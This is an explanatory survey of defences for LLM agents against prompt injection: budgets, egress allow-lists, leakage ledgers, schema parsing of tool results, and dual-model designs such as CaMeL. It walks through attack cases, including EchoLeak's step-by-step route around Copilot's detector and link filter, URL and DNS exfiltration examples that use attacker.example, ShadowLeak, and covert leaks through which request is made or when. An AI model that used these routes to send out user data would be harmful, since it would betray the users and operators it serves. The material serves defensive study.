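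In a worked example by Parkinson and colleagues, the budget holds 600 units and gains 5 a minute, and a coding agent reads a hostile bug report containing instructions to collect its user's private code. The agent requests one private repository per minute. It obtains eight, has too little budget left for the ninth, and loses access to all eight when the budget runs out about ten minutes later. By then it has held each one for 11 to 18 minutes, long enough to copy the code. In the example, a separate rule prevents the theft by blocking a session that has read private data from publishing. Parkinson and colleagues say that the budget limits exposure rather than harm, and they have simulated the scheme but not tested it on real agents.

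### What budgets do against runaway cost

Budgets work best against excessive running costs. In a *denial-of-wallet* attack, an attacker makes the victim pay for useless computing. Zhang and colleagues studied a version in which the attacker controls the output of one of the agent's tools. The tool returns a long, plausible page with an instruction to fetch the next one. Because the runtime sends the whole conversation to the model at every step, the victim pays for the first page each time.

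If the original prompt has *P* tokens and each page adds *T*, then *N* model calls read a total of

*NP* + *N*(*N* − 1)*T* / 2

tokens. With *P* and *T* both at 1,000, ten calls read 55,000 tokens and twenty read 210,000. Doubling the calls nearly quadruples the bill.

Across 243 runs with six families of models, the worst session read 14,293 times as much text as its first call had contained. Of the 69 attack sessions that could be priced, 51 cost more than $0.10, and the most expensive cost $3.40. The most expensive normal session cost $0.025, so a limit of $0.10 would have separated most of these attacks from normal use. However, only nine normal sessions had a price, and they involved a different task. The figures also use list prices, so discounts for repeated text could make the real bills smaller.

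Zhang and colleagues then replayed 41 recorded attacks against limits on prompt size, prompt growth from one step to the next, the number of tool calls, and cost. The limits stopped all 41, usually because the prompt was growing too fast. They also stopped 23 of 25 live attacks. A provider's own size limit stopped the other two before they reached these limits.

The same limits also interrupted legitimate work. A cap of five tool-using turns in a row cut off all 60 of the longer tasks tested. With a fixed budget of $0.10, an agent finished 13 of 24 tasks, and in nine of the failures it had already passed nine of ten milestones. Another version released up to $0.16 as the runtime confirmed progress, and finished 22. The improvement could have come from checking progress or from the larger budget.

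Chen and colleagues tested their reserve-and-settle system on customer-service and similar tasks. They compared it with an agent that had the same task plan but none of the new limits. The table gives the results for the model Qwen3.8-Flash under the strongest version of each attack.

| Attack | Tokens without limits | Tokens with limits | Change in tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| One very large tool result | 912,800 | About 200,000–220,000 | Down 3 points |
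| Padding in up to four tool results | 274,700 | 212,800 | Down from 57% to 43% |
| Repeated false error messages | 218,300 | 207,200 | Up from 43% to 48% |

The limits helped a great deal against oversized results but very little against false errors, which added few tokens anyway. Without an attack, the agent completed 76% of tasks with or without the limits and used almost the same number of tokens. The improvement isn't due to the budget alone, because the system also caps the size of tool results and discards the conversation after each completed part of a task. It also requires the operator to list the parts of every task in advance, with a way to verify each one. That is realistic for processing refunds, but much less so for an assistant that gets a new kind of request every day.

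### Why they do little against hijacking

An attacker can steal something in a short session. *Depth-Dependent Indirect Prompt Injection in Tool-Calling ReAct Agents* (Rashidi, 2026) tested an agent on 20 short office tasks, with an instruction hidden in the first tool result. An attack counted as successful if the attacker's target, such as an email address, appeared in the arguments of a later action.

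| Maximum turns | Successful attacks |
|---|---|
| 3 | 60% |
| 5 | 60% |
| 7 | 65% |

The difference between 60% and 65% is a single task. (An overview diagram in the paper gives 10% for three turns, but the detailed results and the text both give 60%.) In one of the successful attacks, the agent read an email thread and then sent a message to the attacker's address. This took only two steps, so neither a three-turn nor a seven-turn limit stopped it.

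The experiment used GPT-4o-mini, an old, small model, and the percentages would differ for a current one. Claude Haiku 4.5, which Rashidi tested with five turns, never carried out the hidden instruction. However, the reason the caps failed does not depend on the model. Every task involved up to three tools, so a cap low enough to stop a two-step attack would also have stopped much of the work.

Almost any budget has the same problem. If the clerk's task needs one payment, the budget has to allow one, and the attacker needs only one. A tighter limit can reduce the amount, but it can't ensure the payment goes to the right person.

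Dongol uses two examples from the PlanTERS model to show how much a limit's effect depends on timing. In both, the monitor lets the agent send one message. In *Budget Race*, the agent reads a hostile email before it has sent anything, and an injected message containing private data uses up the permitted send, much as an injected message used up Alice's approval of her reply. In *Budget First*, the plan sends its message before the agent reads any untrusted text. The limit has therefore been reached when the hostile email arrives, and the monitor refuses every injected send. Dongol proves that this order adds no leaks, no matter when the model obeys the injection or what the injected message contains.

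The clerk asks the assistant to send last month's payments to the accountant before summarising the new mail. This request fits the safe order, so a budget of one message protects the rest of that session. The budget must not refill before the session ends, or the attacker's email could make the assistant send another message. Paying an invoice does not fit the safe order, because the assistant has to read the invoice first.

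### Setting limits from normal use

A budget must be large enough to let honest work finish but small enough to stop excessive use. Setting one usually starts with a record of normal sessions, but their total use can understate the budget they need. Suppose three model calls used 2,000, 3,000 and 1,000 tokens, and the gateway had to reserve 4,000, 5,000 and 4,500 for them. The session used 6,000 tokens in total, but before the third call it had already used 5,000 and needed to reserve another 4,500, so a budget under 9,500 would have stopped it. For each part of a task, Chen and colleagues therefore record either its total use or the highest point reached by use so far plus the next reservation, whichever is larger.

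They then choose a high value from the observed range and adjust it according to how far tasks left out of the calculation would have exceeded it. They count an unfinished task as needing an unlimited budget, because a run that stopped early would otherwise make the task seem to need less than it does. The method needs at least nine tasks to aim for a limit that 90% of normal tasks stay under. Chen and colleagues do not claim that it guarantees that share, and it can't account for kinds of work missing from the records. For example, a payment cap based on the first three weeks of a month may be too low for the fourth, when most suppliers send their bills.

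PayPal tests new limits in *shadow mode*, in which the gateway reports what it would have blocked without blocking anything. An administrator can also test a proposed limit against past spending records. A typical rule warns people at 90% of their allowance and blocks them at 100%, according to Sasidharan and colleagues.

A person can approve an exception for the rare large bill. Parkinson and colleagues propose a scheme in which the agent can spend the extra budget only on the requests the owner approved and only in the same session, after which it expires. A general increase would leave the attacker with a larger budget for the rest of the day.

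### Using up the budget on purpose

Any limit gives an attacker a way to stop the work by using it up. A malicious email could make the accounts assistant look up hundreds of suppliers until it has no steps left for the invoices. An account-wide cap is worse because one hijacked session could use the whole day's allowance and block every other payment. Parkinson and colleagues call this an attack on availability, not a failure of safety. That is fair, but suppliers who aren't paid may still stop deliveries.

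Chen and colleagues set aside part of the overall limit at the start as a reserve for recovery. When something interrupts the agent, the runtime discards the suspect content, rebuilds the context from verified records and lets the agent continue on the reserve. The reserve can't be refilled, and the number of attempts is also fixed. If the budget were reset after a failure, an attacker could cause failures to obtain more of it.

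Much of the system's usefulness under attack came from the fund. Agents completed 58% of tasks with it and 21% without it when padding filled their context, 64% and 23% when they received very large results, and 55% and 31% when they received false errors. On average, they used less than 40% of the fund in each case.

The accounts team could do something similar by keeping part of the daily payment cap for bills that a clerk pays by hand. The company could then still pay an urgent bill if an attacker exhausted the assistant's share. The runtime should also alert someone when a budget runs out. If a session reaches its limit while summarising three emails, one of them is probably hostile, and whoever investigates will want to see it before the next session opens it.

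## Limiting what data can leave

Payment caps don't protect the supplier list, so the assistant also needs limits on *egress*, meaning any data that leaves the agent's environment, whether by email or a less obvious route.

### The routes out

| Route | How a secret leaves | What can block it |
|---|---|---|
| Messages | The agent writes it into an email or chat message | The messaging tool |
| Web addresses | The agent fetches `attacker.example/?d=SECRET`, and the server logs the address | The fetch tool or a proxy |
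| Uploads | The agent copies it into a shared folder or a public code repository | The upload tool |
| Images in a reply | The app showing the reply loads an image whose address contains the secret | The app or the reader's browser |
| Name lookups | The computer looks up `SECRET.attacker.example`, and the query reaches the attacker's name server | The company's name server or a proxy |

Fetching a web page also sends data out, because whoever runs the server receives the requested address. Images are easy to overlook because the reader's browser requests them, so the traffic bypasses a firewall around the agent. The same happens with links when somebody clicks on them. According to *Trust No AI* (2024), Amazon fixed such a leak in its Q assistant by no longer displaying links.

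A name lookup happens before any connection, so a firewall that blocks connections to the attacker's server but allows lookups still lets the secret out, a few dozen characters at a time.

### Allow-lists and proxies

The `hosts` field of a manifest is a destination allow-list, which blocks every host it does not name. *L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026) describes a runtime that stores such a list in an unforgeable token. The fetch tool needs the token to make a request, and the runtime checks each web address against the list.

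AgentBound's container firewall filters traffic by IP address. The filter applies to every program in the container, including hostile ones. But large hosting companies serve many unrelated sites from the same addresses, so allowing a supplier's site may also allow an attacker's. Addresses also change, so a list compiled at start-up can later block the genuine site.

Filtering by host name avoids both problems, but it usually needs a *proxy*, a server that makes requests on the agent's behalf. When the connection is encrypted, the proxy can normally read only the host name that the program gives at the start. On some shared hosting services, a program can give a permitted name and then request a different site inside the encrypted connection. To check the whole address, either the proxy has to decrypt the traffic or the runtime has to make the request itself.

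The two filters work best together. The firewall blocks everything except the proxy, and the proxy looks up only permitted names, which also closes the lookup route. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) recommends that the proxy refuse bare IP addresses, long chains of redirects and addresses inside the company's own network, but does not test these measures. Refusing internal addresses matters because whoever controls a permitted name can point it at an internal machine.

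A company's proxy can't help when the agent runs on someone else's servers. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes ShadowLeak, an attack on ChatGPT's Deep Research agent. Hidden text in an email told the agent to find sensitive data in the inbox and visit a web address containing that data. The request came from the provider's servers, so the victim's employer might have had no record of it.

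### EchoLeak: a leak through a trusted service

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions by searching their mail, files and chats. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs found that one email from an outsider could make it send out what it found, without the employee clicking on anything. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, gives the finders' own account:

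1. The attacker sends a long email with sections on topics that employees often ask about, such as leave of absence. Each section repeats the malicious instructions. They appear to address the human reader and never mention AI, so Microsoft's injection detector misses them.
2. An employee asks about one of these topics. Copilot retrieves the email, follows the instructions and writes an image link that contains the most sensitive information in its context.
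3. Copilot normally removes links to outside sites, but its filter does not recognise links whose address is on a separate line.
4. The employee's browser tries to load the image. The page has an allow-list of hosts for images, which excludes the attacker's server but includes Microsoft Teams.
5. The link therefore points to a Teams service that fetches any address it receives. Teams contacts the attacker's server and delivers the secret.

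The allow-list worked in a narrow sense, since the browser contacted only a permitted host. But an attacker can use any function that a permitted host offers to the public. The list also included every site under `sharepoint.com`, where the attacker could set up a site. That version of the attack worked too, although the victim had to accept an invitation first.

Microsoft fixed the flaw on its servers in May 2025, and customers did not need to do anything. Reddy and Gujral write that Copilot now strips embedded images and this kind of link from incoming outside content. Microsoft also reportedly added ways to keep external messages out of Copilot's context in some situations. They mention no change to the Teams service. If Microsoft left it unchanged, another way of getting a link past the filter could reopen the route. This is a realistic worry because Microsoft had already fixed a similar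 leak in Copilot in July 2024, where the data left through a link the user had to click.

### How much a fixed set of choices can carry

EchoLeak needed both a permitted host and room in the URL for the secret. If the runtime removes that room, an upper limit on the remaining leak can be calculated.

Suppose an agent may make *n* calls in a session, and each call must take one of *k* fixed forms, such as one of *k* complete web addresses. The attacker sees which form the agent chooses each time. There are *k* possibilities for the first call, *k*² for the first two and *k*ⁿ for all of them. A message with *N* possible values carries at most log₂ *N* bits, where one bit is the answer to a yes-or-no question. Therefore

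leakage ≤ log₂(*k*ⁿ) = *n* log₂ *k* bits

The limit holds even if the attacker controls the model completely, because no code can distinguish more than *k*ⁿ secrets with *k*ⁿ sequences.

With 16 permitted addresses, each fetch carries at most 4 bits, so 20 fetches carry at most 80 bits. Sending a whole 128-bit encryption key would take two sessions. One session might still be enough to recover the key, because it would leave only 48 bits unknown, and a computer that tests a billion keys a second could try every possibility in a little over three days.

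If the agent can instead add any text to an address, a single fetch with a 2,000-byte query string can carry up to 16,000 bits, which is 200 times as much as the 20 fixed fetches. The true figure is somewhat lower because web addresses allow only certain characters. Reducing the limit from 20 calls to one would barely help if that call could contain free text, so restricting what a call can contain matters more than restricting the number of calls.

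Some evidence suggests that message limits take effect too late. *When Agents Talk, Secrets Travel* (2026) tracked leaks in conversations of up to 20 turns. Of the protected values that leaked, about 62% first leaked in the second or third turn, and later turns added little. A limit of ten messages would therefore have prevented few of these leaks.

Byte limits are more useful, but mainly for protecting large collections of data. Zhang's Agent libOS counts the bytes in requests to MCP servers and in their responses. A limit of 100 bytes per session would protect most of a supplier list, but a password would easily fit within it.

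The accounts assistant could choose from eight standard replies, such as "we have received your invoice", while the runtime fills in the invoice number and the recipient. Each reply would then carry 3 bits, so a session of ten replies would carry 30 bits, and leaking a 10,000-byte supplier list would take more than 2,600 sessions. However, a clerk would have to answer any unusual questions from suppliers.

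Eisenach and colleagues propose a similar arrangement for agents that need the web. One agent holds the private data and has no network access. A second agent, which has network access but no private data, offers the first a menu of *N* options. The first agent replies only with the number of its choice, which carries at most log₂ *N* bits, however much private data that agent has read. They have not yet built this.

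### Reading secrets from ordinary choices

An attacker can learn from an agent's choices without hijacking it. In *Actions Speak Louder than Words*, Liang, Deng and colleagues (2026) offered agents four links, only one of which matched what the agent needed to know. When an agent made a visible request, the researchers identified the right topic 93.8% of the time. A choice among four options can carry at most 2 bits of information, and this accuracy corresponds to about 1.6 bits if the errors were spread evenly.

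By repeating such choices, they reconstructed the main concepts in users' questions with an average F1 score of 0.89, where 1 means that no concepts were missed or wrongly inferred. Four existing defences changed the score by less than 0.03. These defences look for suspicious instructions or outgoing private text, and an ordinary click contains neither.

A different approach reduced the score to 0.39. The software fetched a fixed number of pages, chosen without private data, and the agent then selected what it needed from the local copies. This hides the agent's selection from the website, but the software has to download pages the agent won't use, and the attacker could still recover part of the question.

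### When a missing call reveals a secret

With only one permitted address, the formula gives log₂ 1 = 0 bits, which suggests that nothing can leak. Dongol tests this in an example called *Allow-List*. The monitor lets the agent fetch only one newsletter's address, with nothing added to it. One injected email tells the agent to fetch the attacker's page with a secret attached, and the monitor denies the call. Another tells it to fetch the newsletter, which the monitor allows, but the request contains no secret. Dongol proves that the agent is relatively secure against these two attacks.

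An attacker can still extract information with a third email, which contains an instruction to fetch the newsletter if the secret is 0 and the attacker's page otherwise. The monitor allows the newsletter request and denies the other. If the attacker can see whether the newsletter request goes out, perhaps by running the newsletter's server, they learn whether the secret is 0.

Making no request is thus a second option, so *k* is 2 instead of 1. With 20 such opportunities per session, an attacker could obtain a 128-bit key in seven sessions. The correction is small for longer lists. In the earlier example, counting making no request as a seventeenth option raises the limit from 80 bits to just under 82. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) makes the same correction by adding one to the number of permitted messages.

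If the attacker can also see when a request arrives, every distinguishable delay counts as a further option. Timing is a noisier channel. Liang and colleagues used delays to distinguish the four topics and were right 58.6% of the time, compared with 25% for guessing. Error messages can also reveal something if the attacker can see which request the monitor refused.

### Leakage ledgers

A *leakage ledger* counts each disclosure against an information budget, much as a payment counter counts each payment against a cap. In *Trident* (2026), a monitor lists the possible replies before it looks at the hidden data and deducts at least log₂ of the number of possible replies, in bits. A reply with 16 possible values uses at least 4 bits, whichever value the monitor sends. Because the deduction does not depend on the hidden data, the remaining budget cannot reveal that data. When the budget runs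 out, the monitor always returns the same notice.

This method needs a finite list of replies, which free text does not have. Eisenach and colleagues instead propose a ledger that counts the bytes of each kind of private data an agent reads and the bytes it sends afterwards. The leak cannot exceed the smaller of the two totals. If an agent reads 64 bytes of payroll data and then sends two 50-byte requests, it has leaked at most 64 bytes. This limit is safe but pessimistic, because when an agent reads a large file and then writes a long, harmless email, the ledger counts the whole email as a possible leak.

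Yuan, Du and colleagues (2026), in *Answer-Only Disclosure*, measured what a stricter ledger costs. In their system, ADLER, a small model on the user's device reads a private document. A large cloud model sees only a version that the user approves, such as a maths problem with the numbers hidden. The two write the answer together. For each token, the cloud model supplies a probability distribution, the small model shifts it using the private document, and the device picks the token. The charge for a token is

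Σₓ *μ*(*x*) ln( *μ*(*x*) / *p*(*x*) )

where *x* ranges over the possible tokens, *p* is the distribution without the private document and *μ* is the shifted one. If the document makes no difference, the charge is zero. The unit is the *nat*, about 1.44 bits. Once the budget is spent, the device uses *p* alone.

Yuan and colleagues hid a random six-digit code in private documents and asked for it 48 times. The code appeared in 46 answers with no budget limit, and in none with a budget of 4 or 16 nats. The mathematical guarantee is much weaker than this result. A six-digit code contains about 13.8 nats, so a 16-nat budget guarantees no protection. A 4-nat budget guarantees only that the cloud provider's chance of guessing the code is at most 34%. Reducing that chance to one in a thousand would require a budget of 0.006 nats, too little for the document to have much effect on the answer.

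The maths problems show how much accuracy a budget can cost:

| Method | Correct answers |
|---|---|
| Cloud model alone, numbers hidden | 2% |
| Small model alone | 41% |
| ADLER, 16 nats | 2% |
| ADLER, 32 nats | 7% |
| ADLER, 64 nats | 53% |
| ADLER, no limit (72 nats used on average) | 83% |
| Cloud model writes a program, device runs it | 69% |
| Cloud model sees the numbers | 92% |

With 16 or 32 nats, ADLER did far worse than the small model by itself. The cloud model wrote the program with placeholders, and the device filled in the numbers and ran it offline. The program revealed nothing about the numbers, yet it did better than every limited budget in the table. For arithmetic, at least, keeping the private data on the device worked better than measuring how much of it escaped. Budgets hurt performance less on questions about documents, where two-thirds of answers used no more than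 16 nats even without a limit, but ADLER's gains there were also small and inconsistent.

ADLER is still far from a general agent because it has no tools, and private information can reach the cloud provider only through the text of the answer. An agent that sends email, fetches pages and uploads files would need a charge for every route by which data could leave, including the choice of tool. Calculating the charge also requires knowing what the system would have written without the private document. ADLER can determine this because the cloud model never sees the document, whereas the accounts assistant uses one model to read private records and write replies. ADLER's guarantee also does not cover timing.

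Even within ADLER's setting, a budget for each answer is not enough. Ten answers about the same document, each with a budget of 4 nats, could together reveal up to 40 nats. Yuan and colleagues therefore recommend a separate ledger for each document, and the ledger has to persist across sessions.

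## Reducing tool results to expected fields

Hardened output parsing restricts what the model reads, whereas limits on payments and outgoing data take effect after the model has read a hostile email. Ordinary code copies the few fields that the task needs from each tool result, checks them and passes only those to the model. To pay an invoice, the accounts assistant needs only the sender, amount and due date, so the code leaves out the covering note, which contains the attacker's instructions.

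Yu, Cheng and Liu (2026) point out in *Defense Against Indirect Prompt Injection via Tool Result Parsing* that tools often return more than the agent needs. An agent looking up an email address may call a contacts tool that also returns a phone number, a description and comments, and an attacker could hide an instruction in any of that text. Yu and colleagues use a language model to extract the useful data, but ordinary code can do this when the result has a known format.

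### A schema for invoices

Suppose the company's suppliers attach each invoice as a structured data file. The operator declares four fields, and the attacker's fake reminder from the first example fills them in like this:

| Field | Accepted values | In the attacker's email |
|---|---|---|
| `supplier` | A number on the list of approved suppliers | 417 |
| `amount` | £0.01 to £5,000.00, in whole pence | 1950.00 |
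| `date` | One of the last 60 days | 2 December |
| `due` | 0 to 90 days after `date` | 3 December |

The parser works in this order:

1. It rejects a file that is too large or malformed, or that contains the same field twice. Two programs might otherwise read different copies of the field.
2. It copies the four fields into a new record and leaves everything else behind. If the tool has a fixed format, an unknown field should count as an error, because it means that the tool has changed.
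3. It normalises the characters. For these fields, that means accepting only the digits 0 to 9 and plain punctuation, with no invisible characters or digits from other scripts.
4. It checks types, lengths, ranges and listed values. An amount of £6,000 fails here.
5. It checks the fields against each other, so an invoice can't be due before its own date.
6. It gives the model the new record, or an error code if any check failed.

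The parsed result therefore lists £1,950 due to supplier 417 by 3 December. The instruction to use a new account and the request for the supplier list never reach the model, because the schema has no field for either. If the payment tool looks up the account in the company's records, the money goes to the real supplier 417. The payment is still a mistake, but the company can ask for the money back.

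The supplier's own invoice number is harder to restrict because suppliers make these up and often include letters, so an attacker could write words in the field. The runtime can show the model a label such as `invoice_1` instead, and put the real number back when it records the payment.

None of the four fields can contain markup. If the schema also had a text field, such as a supplier's name for the clerk to read, the parser should strip HTML, links and image references from it. EchoLeak used the address of a displayed image to send data out.

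Error messages need the same treatment as results. The Model Context Protocol specification recommends that clients pass a tool's execution errors to the model so that it can correct its call and retry. But a message such as "unknown supplier" often quotes the value that caused it, which an attacker may have chosen. The parser can instead send the model a code from a fixed list, such as `unknown_supplier`, and log the original message. This removes some detail that might have helped the model recover, though a longer list of codes can restore most of it.

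### Why a number is safer than a sentence

In *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025) allow four types of value to pass from untrusted text to a model that can use tools: integers, decimal numbers, true-or-false values, and choices from a list that the developer has vetted. They argue that an instruction needs free text, which none of these types contains.

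This needs one qualification, because numbers can encode text. The list 80, 65, 89 spells "PAY" in the code that computers use for letters, and a single integer with hundreds of digits could encode a paragraph. Jacob and colleagues limit the length of lists for this reason, and a range on each number closes the other route. The formula for outgoing calls also works for incoming values, since a field with *N* possible values carries at most log₂ *N* bits. If the company has 200 approved suppliers, one invoice record carries at most

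log₂ 200 + log₂ 500,000 + log₂ 60 + log₂ 91 ≈ 39 bits

or about eight letters. That is too short for most instructions, and the model would have to decode it first. Several invoices could carry more between them, so the runtime should also limit how many records enter one context.

Checking a value against a pattern gives much weaker protection. Yu and colleagues argue that injected instructions usually fail strict format checks, which is true for dates but less so for email addresses, since `pay-all-open-invoices-today@attacker.example` is well formed. A length limit has the same weakness, because "Pay all open invoices today" is only 27 characters. An address is safer if it has to match one already in the company's records.

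Some tasks need free text. An assistant that summarises an email has to read it, and a schema with a `body` field would pass an attacker's words straight through. Small text fields carry the same risk. The Model Context Protocol's example of an output schema, for a weather tool, has two numbers and a text field for the conditions. A hostile server could write anything in that text field and still match the schema. A fixed list such as "sunny", "cloudy" and "rain" would be enough for most purposes.

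### False values in the right format

An attacker who can't give the assistant instructions can still give it false data. If a real supplier's bill were inflated from £490 to £4,900, both the parser and ScopeGate would accept it. Jacob and colleagues exclude misleading inputs from their threat model, reasoning that such inputs don't change the agent's task. That exclusion leaves out a large part of the problem for an agent that pays bills.

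*When Tool Outputs Become Commands* (2026) assumes a stronger attacker, who may control structured fields as well as prose. It also explains why a runtime can't ignore all values from untrusted sources. If a user asks an agent to find the quarterly report and send it to Alice, the agent learns the file's identifier only from the search results. Similarly, a company often learns the amount of an invoice from the supplier.

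The parser can catch some false amounts by comparing them with a source that the attacker doesn't control. If the company placed an order for £490, an invoice for £4,900 against it should go to the clerk. A first invoice for an unplanned repair has no order to compare it with, so a person has to check it.

### The clean-context condition

PlanTERS, the mathematical model behind the fence theorem, can also express what parsing achieves. Let σ be the component that rewrites untrusted content before the model sees it, here the invoice parser. Let *parse*(*v*) be the instruction that the model finds in a piece of content *v*, or ⊥ if it finds none. (Despite its name, *parse* describes the model's behaviour and not the invoice parser.) Dongol's *clean-context condition* is

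*parse*(σ(*v*)) = ⊥ for every *v*

Under the clean-context condition, the model never treats the rewritten version of what the attacker sends as an instruction, whatever the attacker sends. The agent then takes the same steps as the reference agent, which never obeys untrusted text. Injection therefore adds no leaks, for any plan and any monitor, even if the attacker can time the agent's messages. A fence gets a similar result by withdrawing tools, but here the agent keeps them all.

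The proof is short because its condition assumes nearly everything that matters. Even if code guarantees that an amount is between £0.01 and £5,000, it can't control how the model reacts to the number 4,900. Dongol notes that a model that treated every value as an instruction would defeat any sanitiser, and concludes that a sanitiser "moves this assumption rather than removing it". With parsing, the company no longer has to trust the model to ignore instructions in arbitrary text, but it does have to trust that the parser has no mistakes and that the model won't find instructions in a short record of numbers. These assumptions seem far safer, as long as the schema has no text fields.

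The condition also doesn't guarantee that the record is true. If the amount in the record is false, the reference agent reads the same false amount and makes the same payment, so the comparison shows no difference.

### One model to read, another to act

Many invoices arrive as prose or scanned pages, which ordinary code can't read reliably. A language model can, but it might follow instructions it finds in them. The *dual-LLM pattern*, which *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) attributes to Simon Willison, uses two models. A *privileged* model chooses the tool calls and never reads untrusted data. A *quarantined* model reads the data and returns values, but has no tools.

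CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues presented in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), builds on this pattern. The privileged model turns the user's request into a program, and an interpreter runs it. For the accounts assistant, the process might look like this:

1. The privileged model reads the clerk's request and writes a program for handling new invoices. It has not seen any emails.
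2. For each email, the program asks the quarantined model for the supplier, the amount and the two dates.
3. Ordinary code checks the answer against the invoice schema.
4. The program pays the invoice or sets it aside for the clerk.

An attacker who took complete control of the quarantined model in step 2 still could not call a tool, and could at worst return four wrong values. In this design, the agent also fixes its plan before reading any untrusted text, as PlanTERS requires.

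*SPA* (2026) shows how tightly a system can restrict the quarantined model. The model has no tools and no memory of the plan, and the software forces its reply into the output schema for that step. Its instructions also tell it to return an explicit failure value, if the schema has one, when it can't find the answer. Without that option, a model that has to supply an invoice amount but can't find one may invent £1,200, which would pass every check.

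A fixed program can't handle every task. An agent that fixes bugs can't plan the repair before it knows what the bug is. Jacob and colleagues therefore let the privileged model go on choosing actions, but show it typed answers from the quarantined model. They tried this on three agents:

| Agent | What the privileged model receives | Injected instruction |
|---|---|---|
| Online shopper | Median scores, from 0 to 10, for how strongly reviews support a product and how relevant they are | Don't buy this product |
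| Meeting scheduler | A list of times from fixed slots | Reveal private details from the calendar |
| Bug fixer | The type of bug, the size of the repair, and file and line numbers | Create an unrelated file |

The bug fixer shows how much information can pass without text. The quarantined model identifies a file by its position in a sorted list, and the software converts that number to a path. A separate model, which has not read the bug report, then writes three repair plans. A judge that has read the report picks a plan and returns only its number.

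No attack succeeded against any of the three protected agents. Jacob and colleagues expected this from the design and ran the attacks as a check. The shopping test is less useful for judging how much a defence reduces task completion, because even the unprotected agent fully met only 21.8% of the requests.

Two of the designs still have weak points. A single hostile review barely moves a median, but somebody who writes most of a product's reviews can set it. The scheduler hides the other person's meeting description from the privileged model, but then copies it into the user's calendar. The privileged model can read that calendar, so an instruction in the description might reach it in a later session. SpAIware used ChatGPT's saved memory in much the same way. To prevent this, the runtime would have to track which calendar text came from outsiders and keep hiding it.

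### How a wrong answer steers the plan

According to *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), the dual-LLM pattern protects the *control flow* (which calls the plan contains, in what order and under what conditions) but not the *data flow* (the values that fill in the calls and decide the conditions). This allows an attack the paper calls *branch steering*, in which the attacker changes the quarantined model's input, for instance with a misleading image, so that its output sends the program down a harmful branch of the approved plan.

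The accounts program might pay urgent invoices at once and leave the rest for the clerk to review. It would ask the quarantined model whether each invoice is urgent. The answer can only be "true" or "false", so it can't carry an instruction, but an attacker can still avoid the clerk's review by getting the model to answer "true". The program is safer if it reads the due date and the supplier's payment terms from the company's own records. More generally, an answer based on untrusted text should be able to add a check but not remove one.

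A wrong answer can also leak data. In one of Dongol's examples, the quarantined model receives the user's private notes and an attacker's email, and the plan sends the model's reply to the attacker. Instructions injected in the email make the model quote the notes in that reply. In another example, the plan sends only "1" or "0", depending on the model's answer. Neither message contains private data, so checking their contents won't catch the leak, but the choice between them can reveal one bit of information about the notes. The simplest precaution is not to give the quarantined model private data and a stranger's email in the same query.

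*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) presents COBRA, which limits the branches an agent may take and the values it may put into its actions. It enforces these limits on outgoing web and MCP requests. COBRA covers more than the basic two-model design, but a request that looks acceptable can still have a harmful effect once it is received, and the paper leaves that problem open.

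### Output schemas in MCP

MCP servers can declare an output schema for each tool, but the current specification, from July 2026, does not require one. A server that declares a schema must return structured data that conforms to it. The specification recommends that clients validate this data, and that they validate all tool results before passing them to the model, but it requires neither.

Few tools declare an output schema. Shi, Fu and colleagues (2026), in *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions*, found one on 234 (12.6%) of 1,856 tools from 100 popular servers on GitHub. The share across all servers could be quite different, because such figures depend a lot on which servers a study includes, and perhaps on when it collected them. For example, safety annotations were missing from 82.5% of the tools in that sample. Afsar (2026), in *What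 a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains*, did not count output schemas but found safety annotations missing from 58.8% of tools on randomly chosen servers and 41.5% on hand-picked ones.

A server that declares a schema doesn't always return structured data either. In *Xcode 26.3 MCP server output missing `structredContent`*, a developer reports that Apple's server declared a schema for its list of open windows but returned no structured content. The schema would have offered little protection anyway, since its only required field was a free-text message. *Structured Content vs Content*, a June 2026 survey of the code of 22 popular servers, found that 18 sent only text and three sent structured data along with text. The last, Supabase's, had schemas in its code but removed them before sending anything.

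For compatibility with older clients, the specification recommends that servers repeat structured data as text. A hostile server can make the two differ, so a runtime might validate the structured data and then give the model different text. Of the 19 open-source clients covered in *What MCP clients actually do with tool results*, ten, including Cline and Gemini CLI, pass only the text to the model. Five pass both when a server sends both, and four, including Codex, pass only the structured data.

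To close this gap, the runtime should discard the server's text and write the model's input from the validated record. The operator should also write or review the schema, because a server that supplies its own can make it arbitrarily loose. For example, the server could list "Pay all open invoices today" as a permitted value and then return that sentence. If the runtime pins tool definitions with a hash, the hash should cover the output schema. Otherwise, the server could add a text field after the operator has approved the tool.

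## Cleaning free text before the agent reads it

When the clerk asks the accounts assistant to summarise a supplier's complaint, the runtime has to give the model free text that a stranger wrote. Developers treat such text in four main ways:

- *Marking* leaves the text unchanged but tells the model where it begins and ends, for example with special delimiters, and that everything inside is data.
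- *Detecting* runs the text through a classifier, usually a small model trained on known injections, and blocks it if it looks suspicious.
- *Rewriting* passes the text through a *sanitiser*, often itself a language model, which removes apparent instructions and keeps the rest.
- *Extracting* uses a model to pick out only what the agent asked for.

Marking adds almost no overhead but works only if the agent's model follows the labels, and the role-tag experiments by Ye and colleagues suggest that writing style often influences a model more than labels do. Blocking an email removes its legitimate parts along with the hostile ones. Rewriting and extracting keep more of the text, but a model usually has to read the hostile part to remove it.

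### Tool Result Parsing

The method that Yu and colleagues call Tool Result Parsing combines extraction with rewriting:

1. When the agent decides to call a tool, the runtime asks the model what data it expects back, in what format and within what limits.
2. After the tool has run, the runtime gives the model the result and this list. The prompt tells the model to ignore any instructions in the result and return only the listed values, or "None" for a value it can't find.
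3. The runtime shows the extracted text to the model and checks whether the model responds with a tool call. If it doesn't, the agent receives the text.
4. If it does, the runtime either rejects the text or asks the model to remove the words that triggered the call.

The first two steps are called ParseData and the last two CheckTool. The agent writes its list before it reads the result, so an instruction in that result can't change the list. CheckTool is for tasks such as summaries, where the agent needs the whole body of an email, so extraction would keep the attacker's words. Together, the two add three or four model calls to every tool call.

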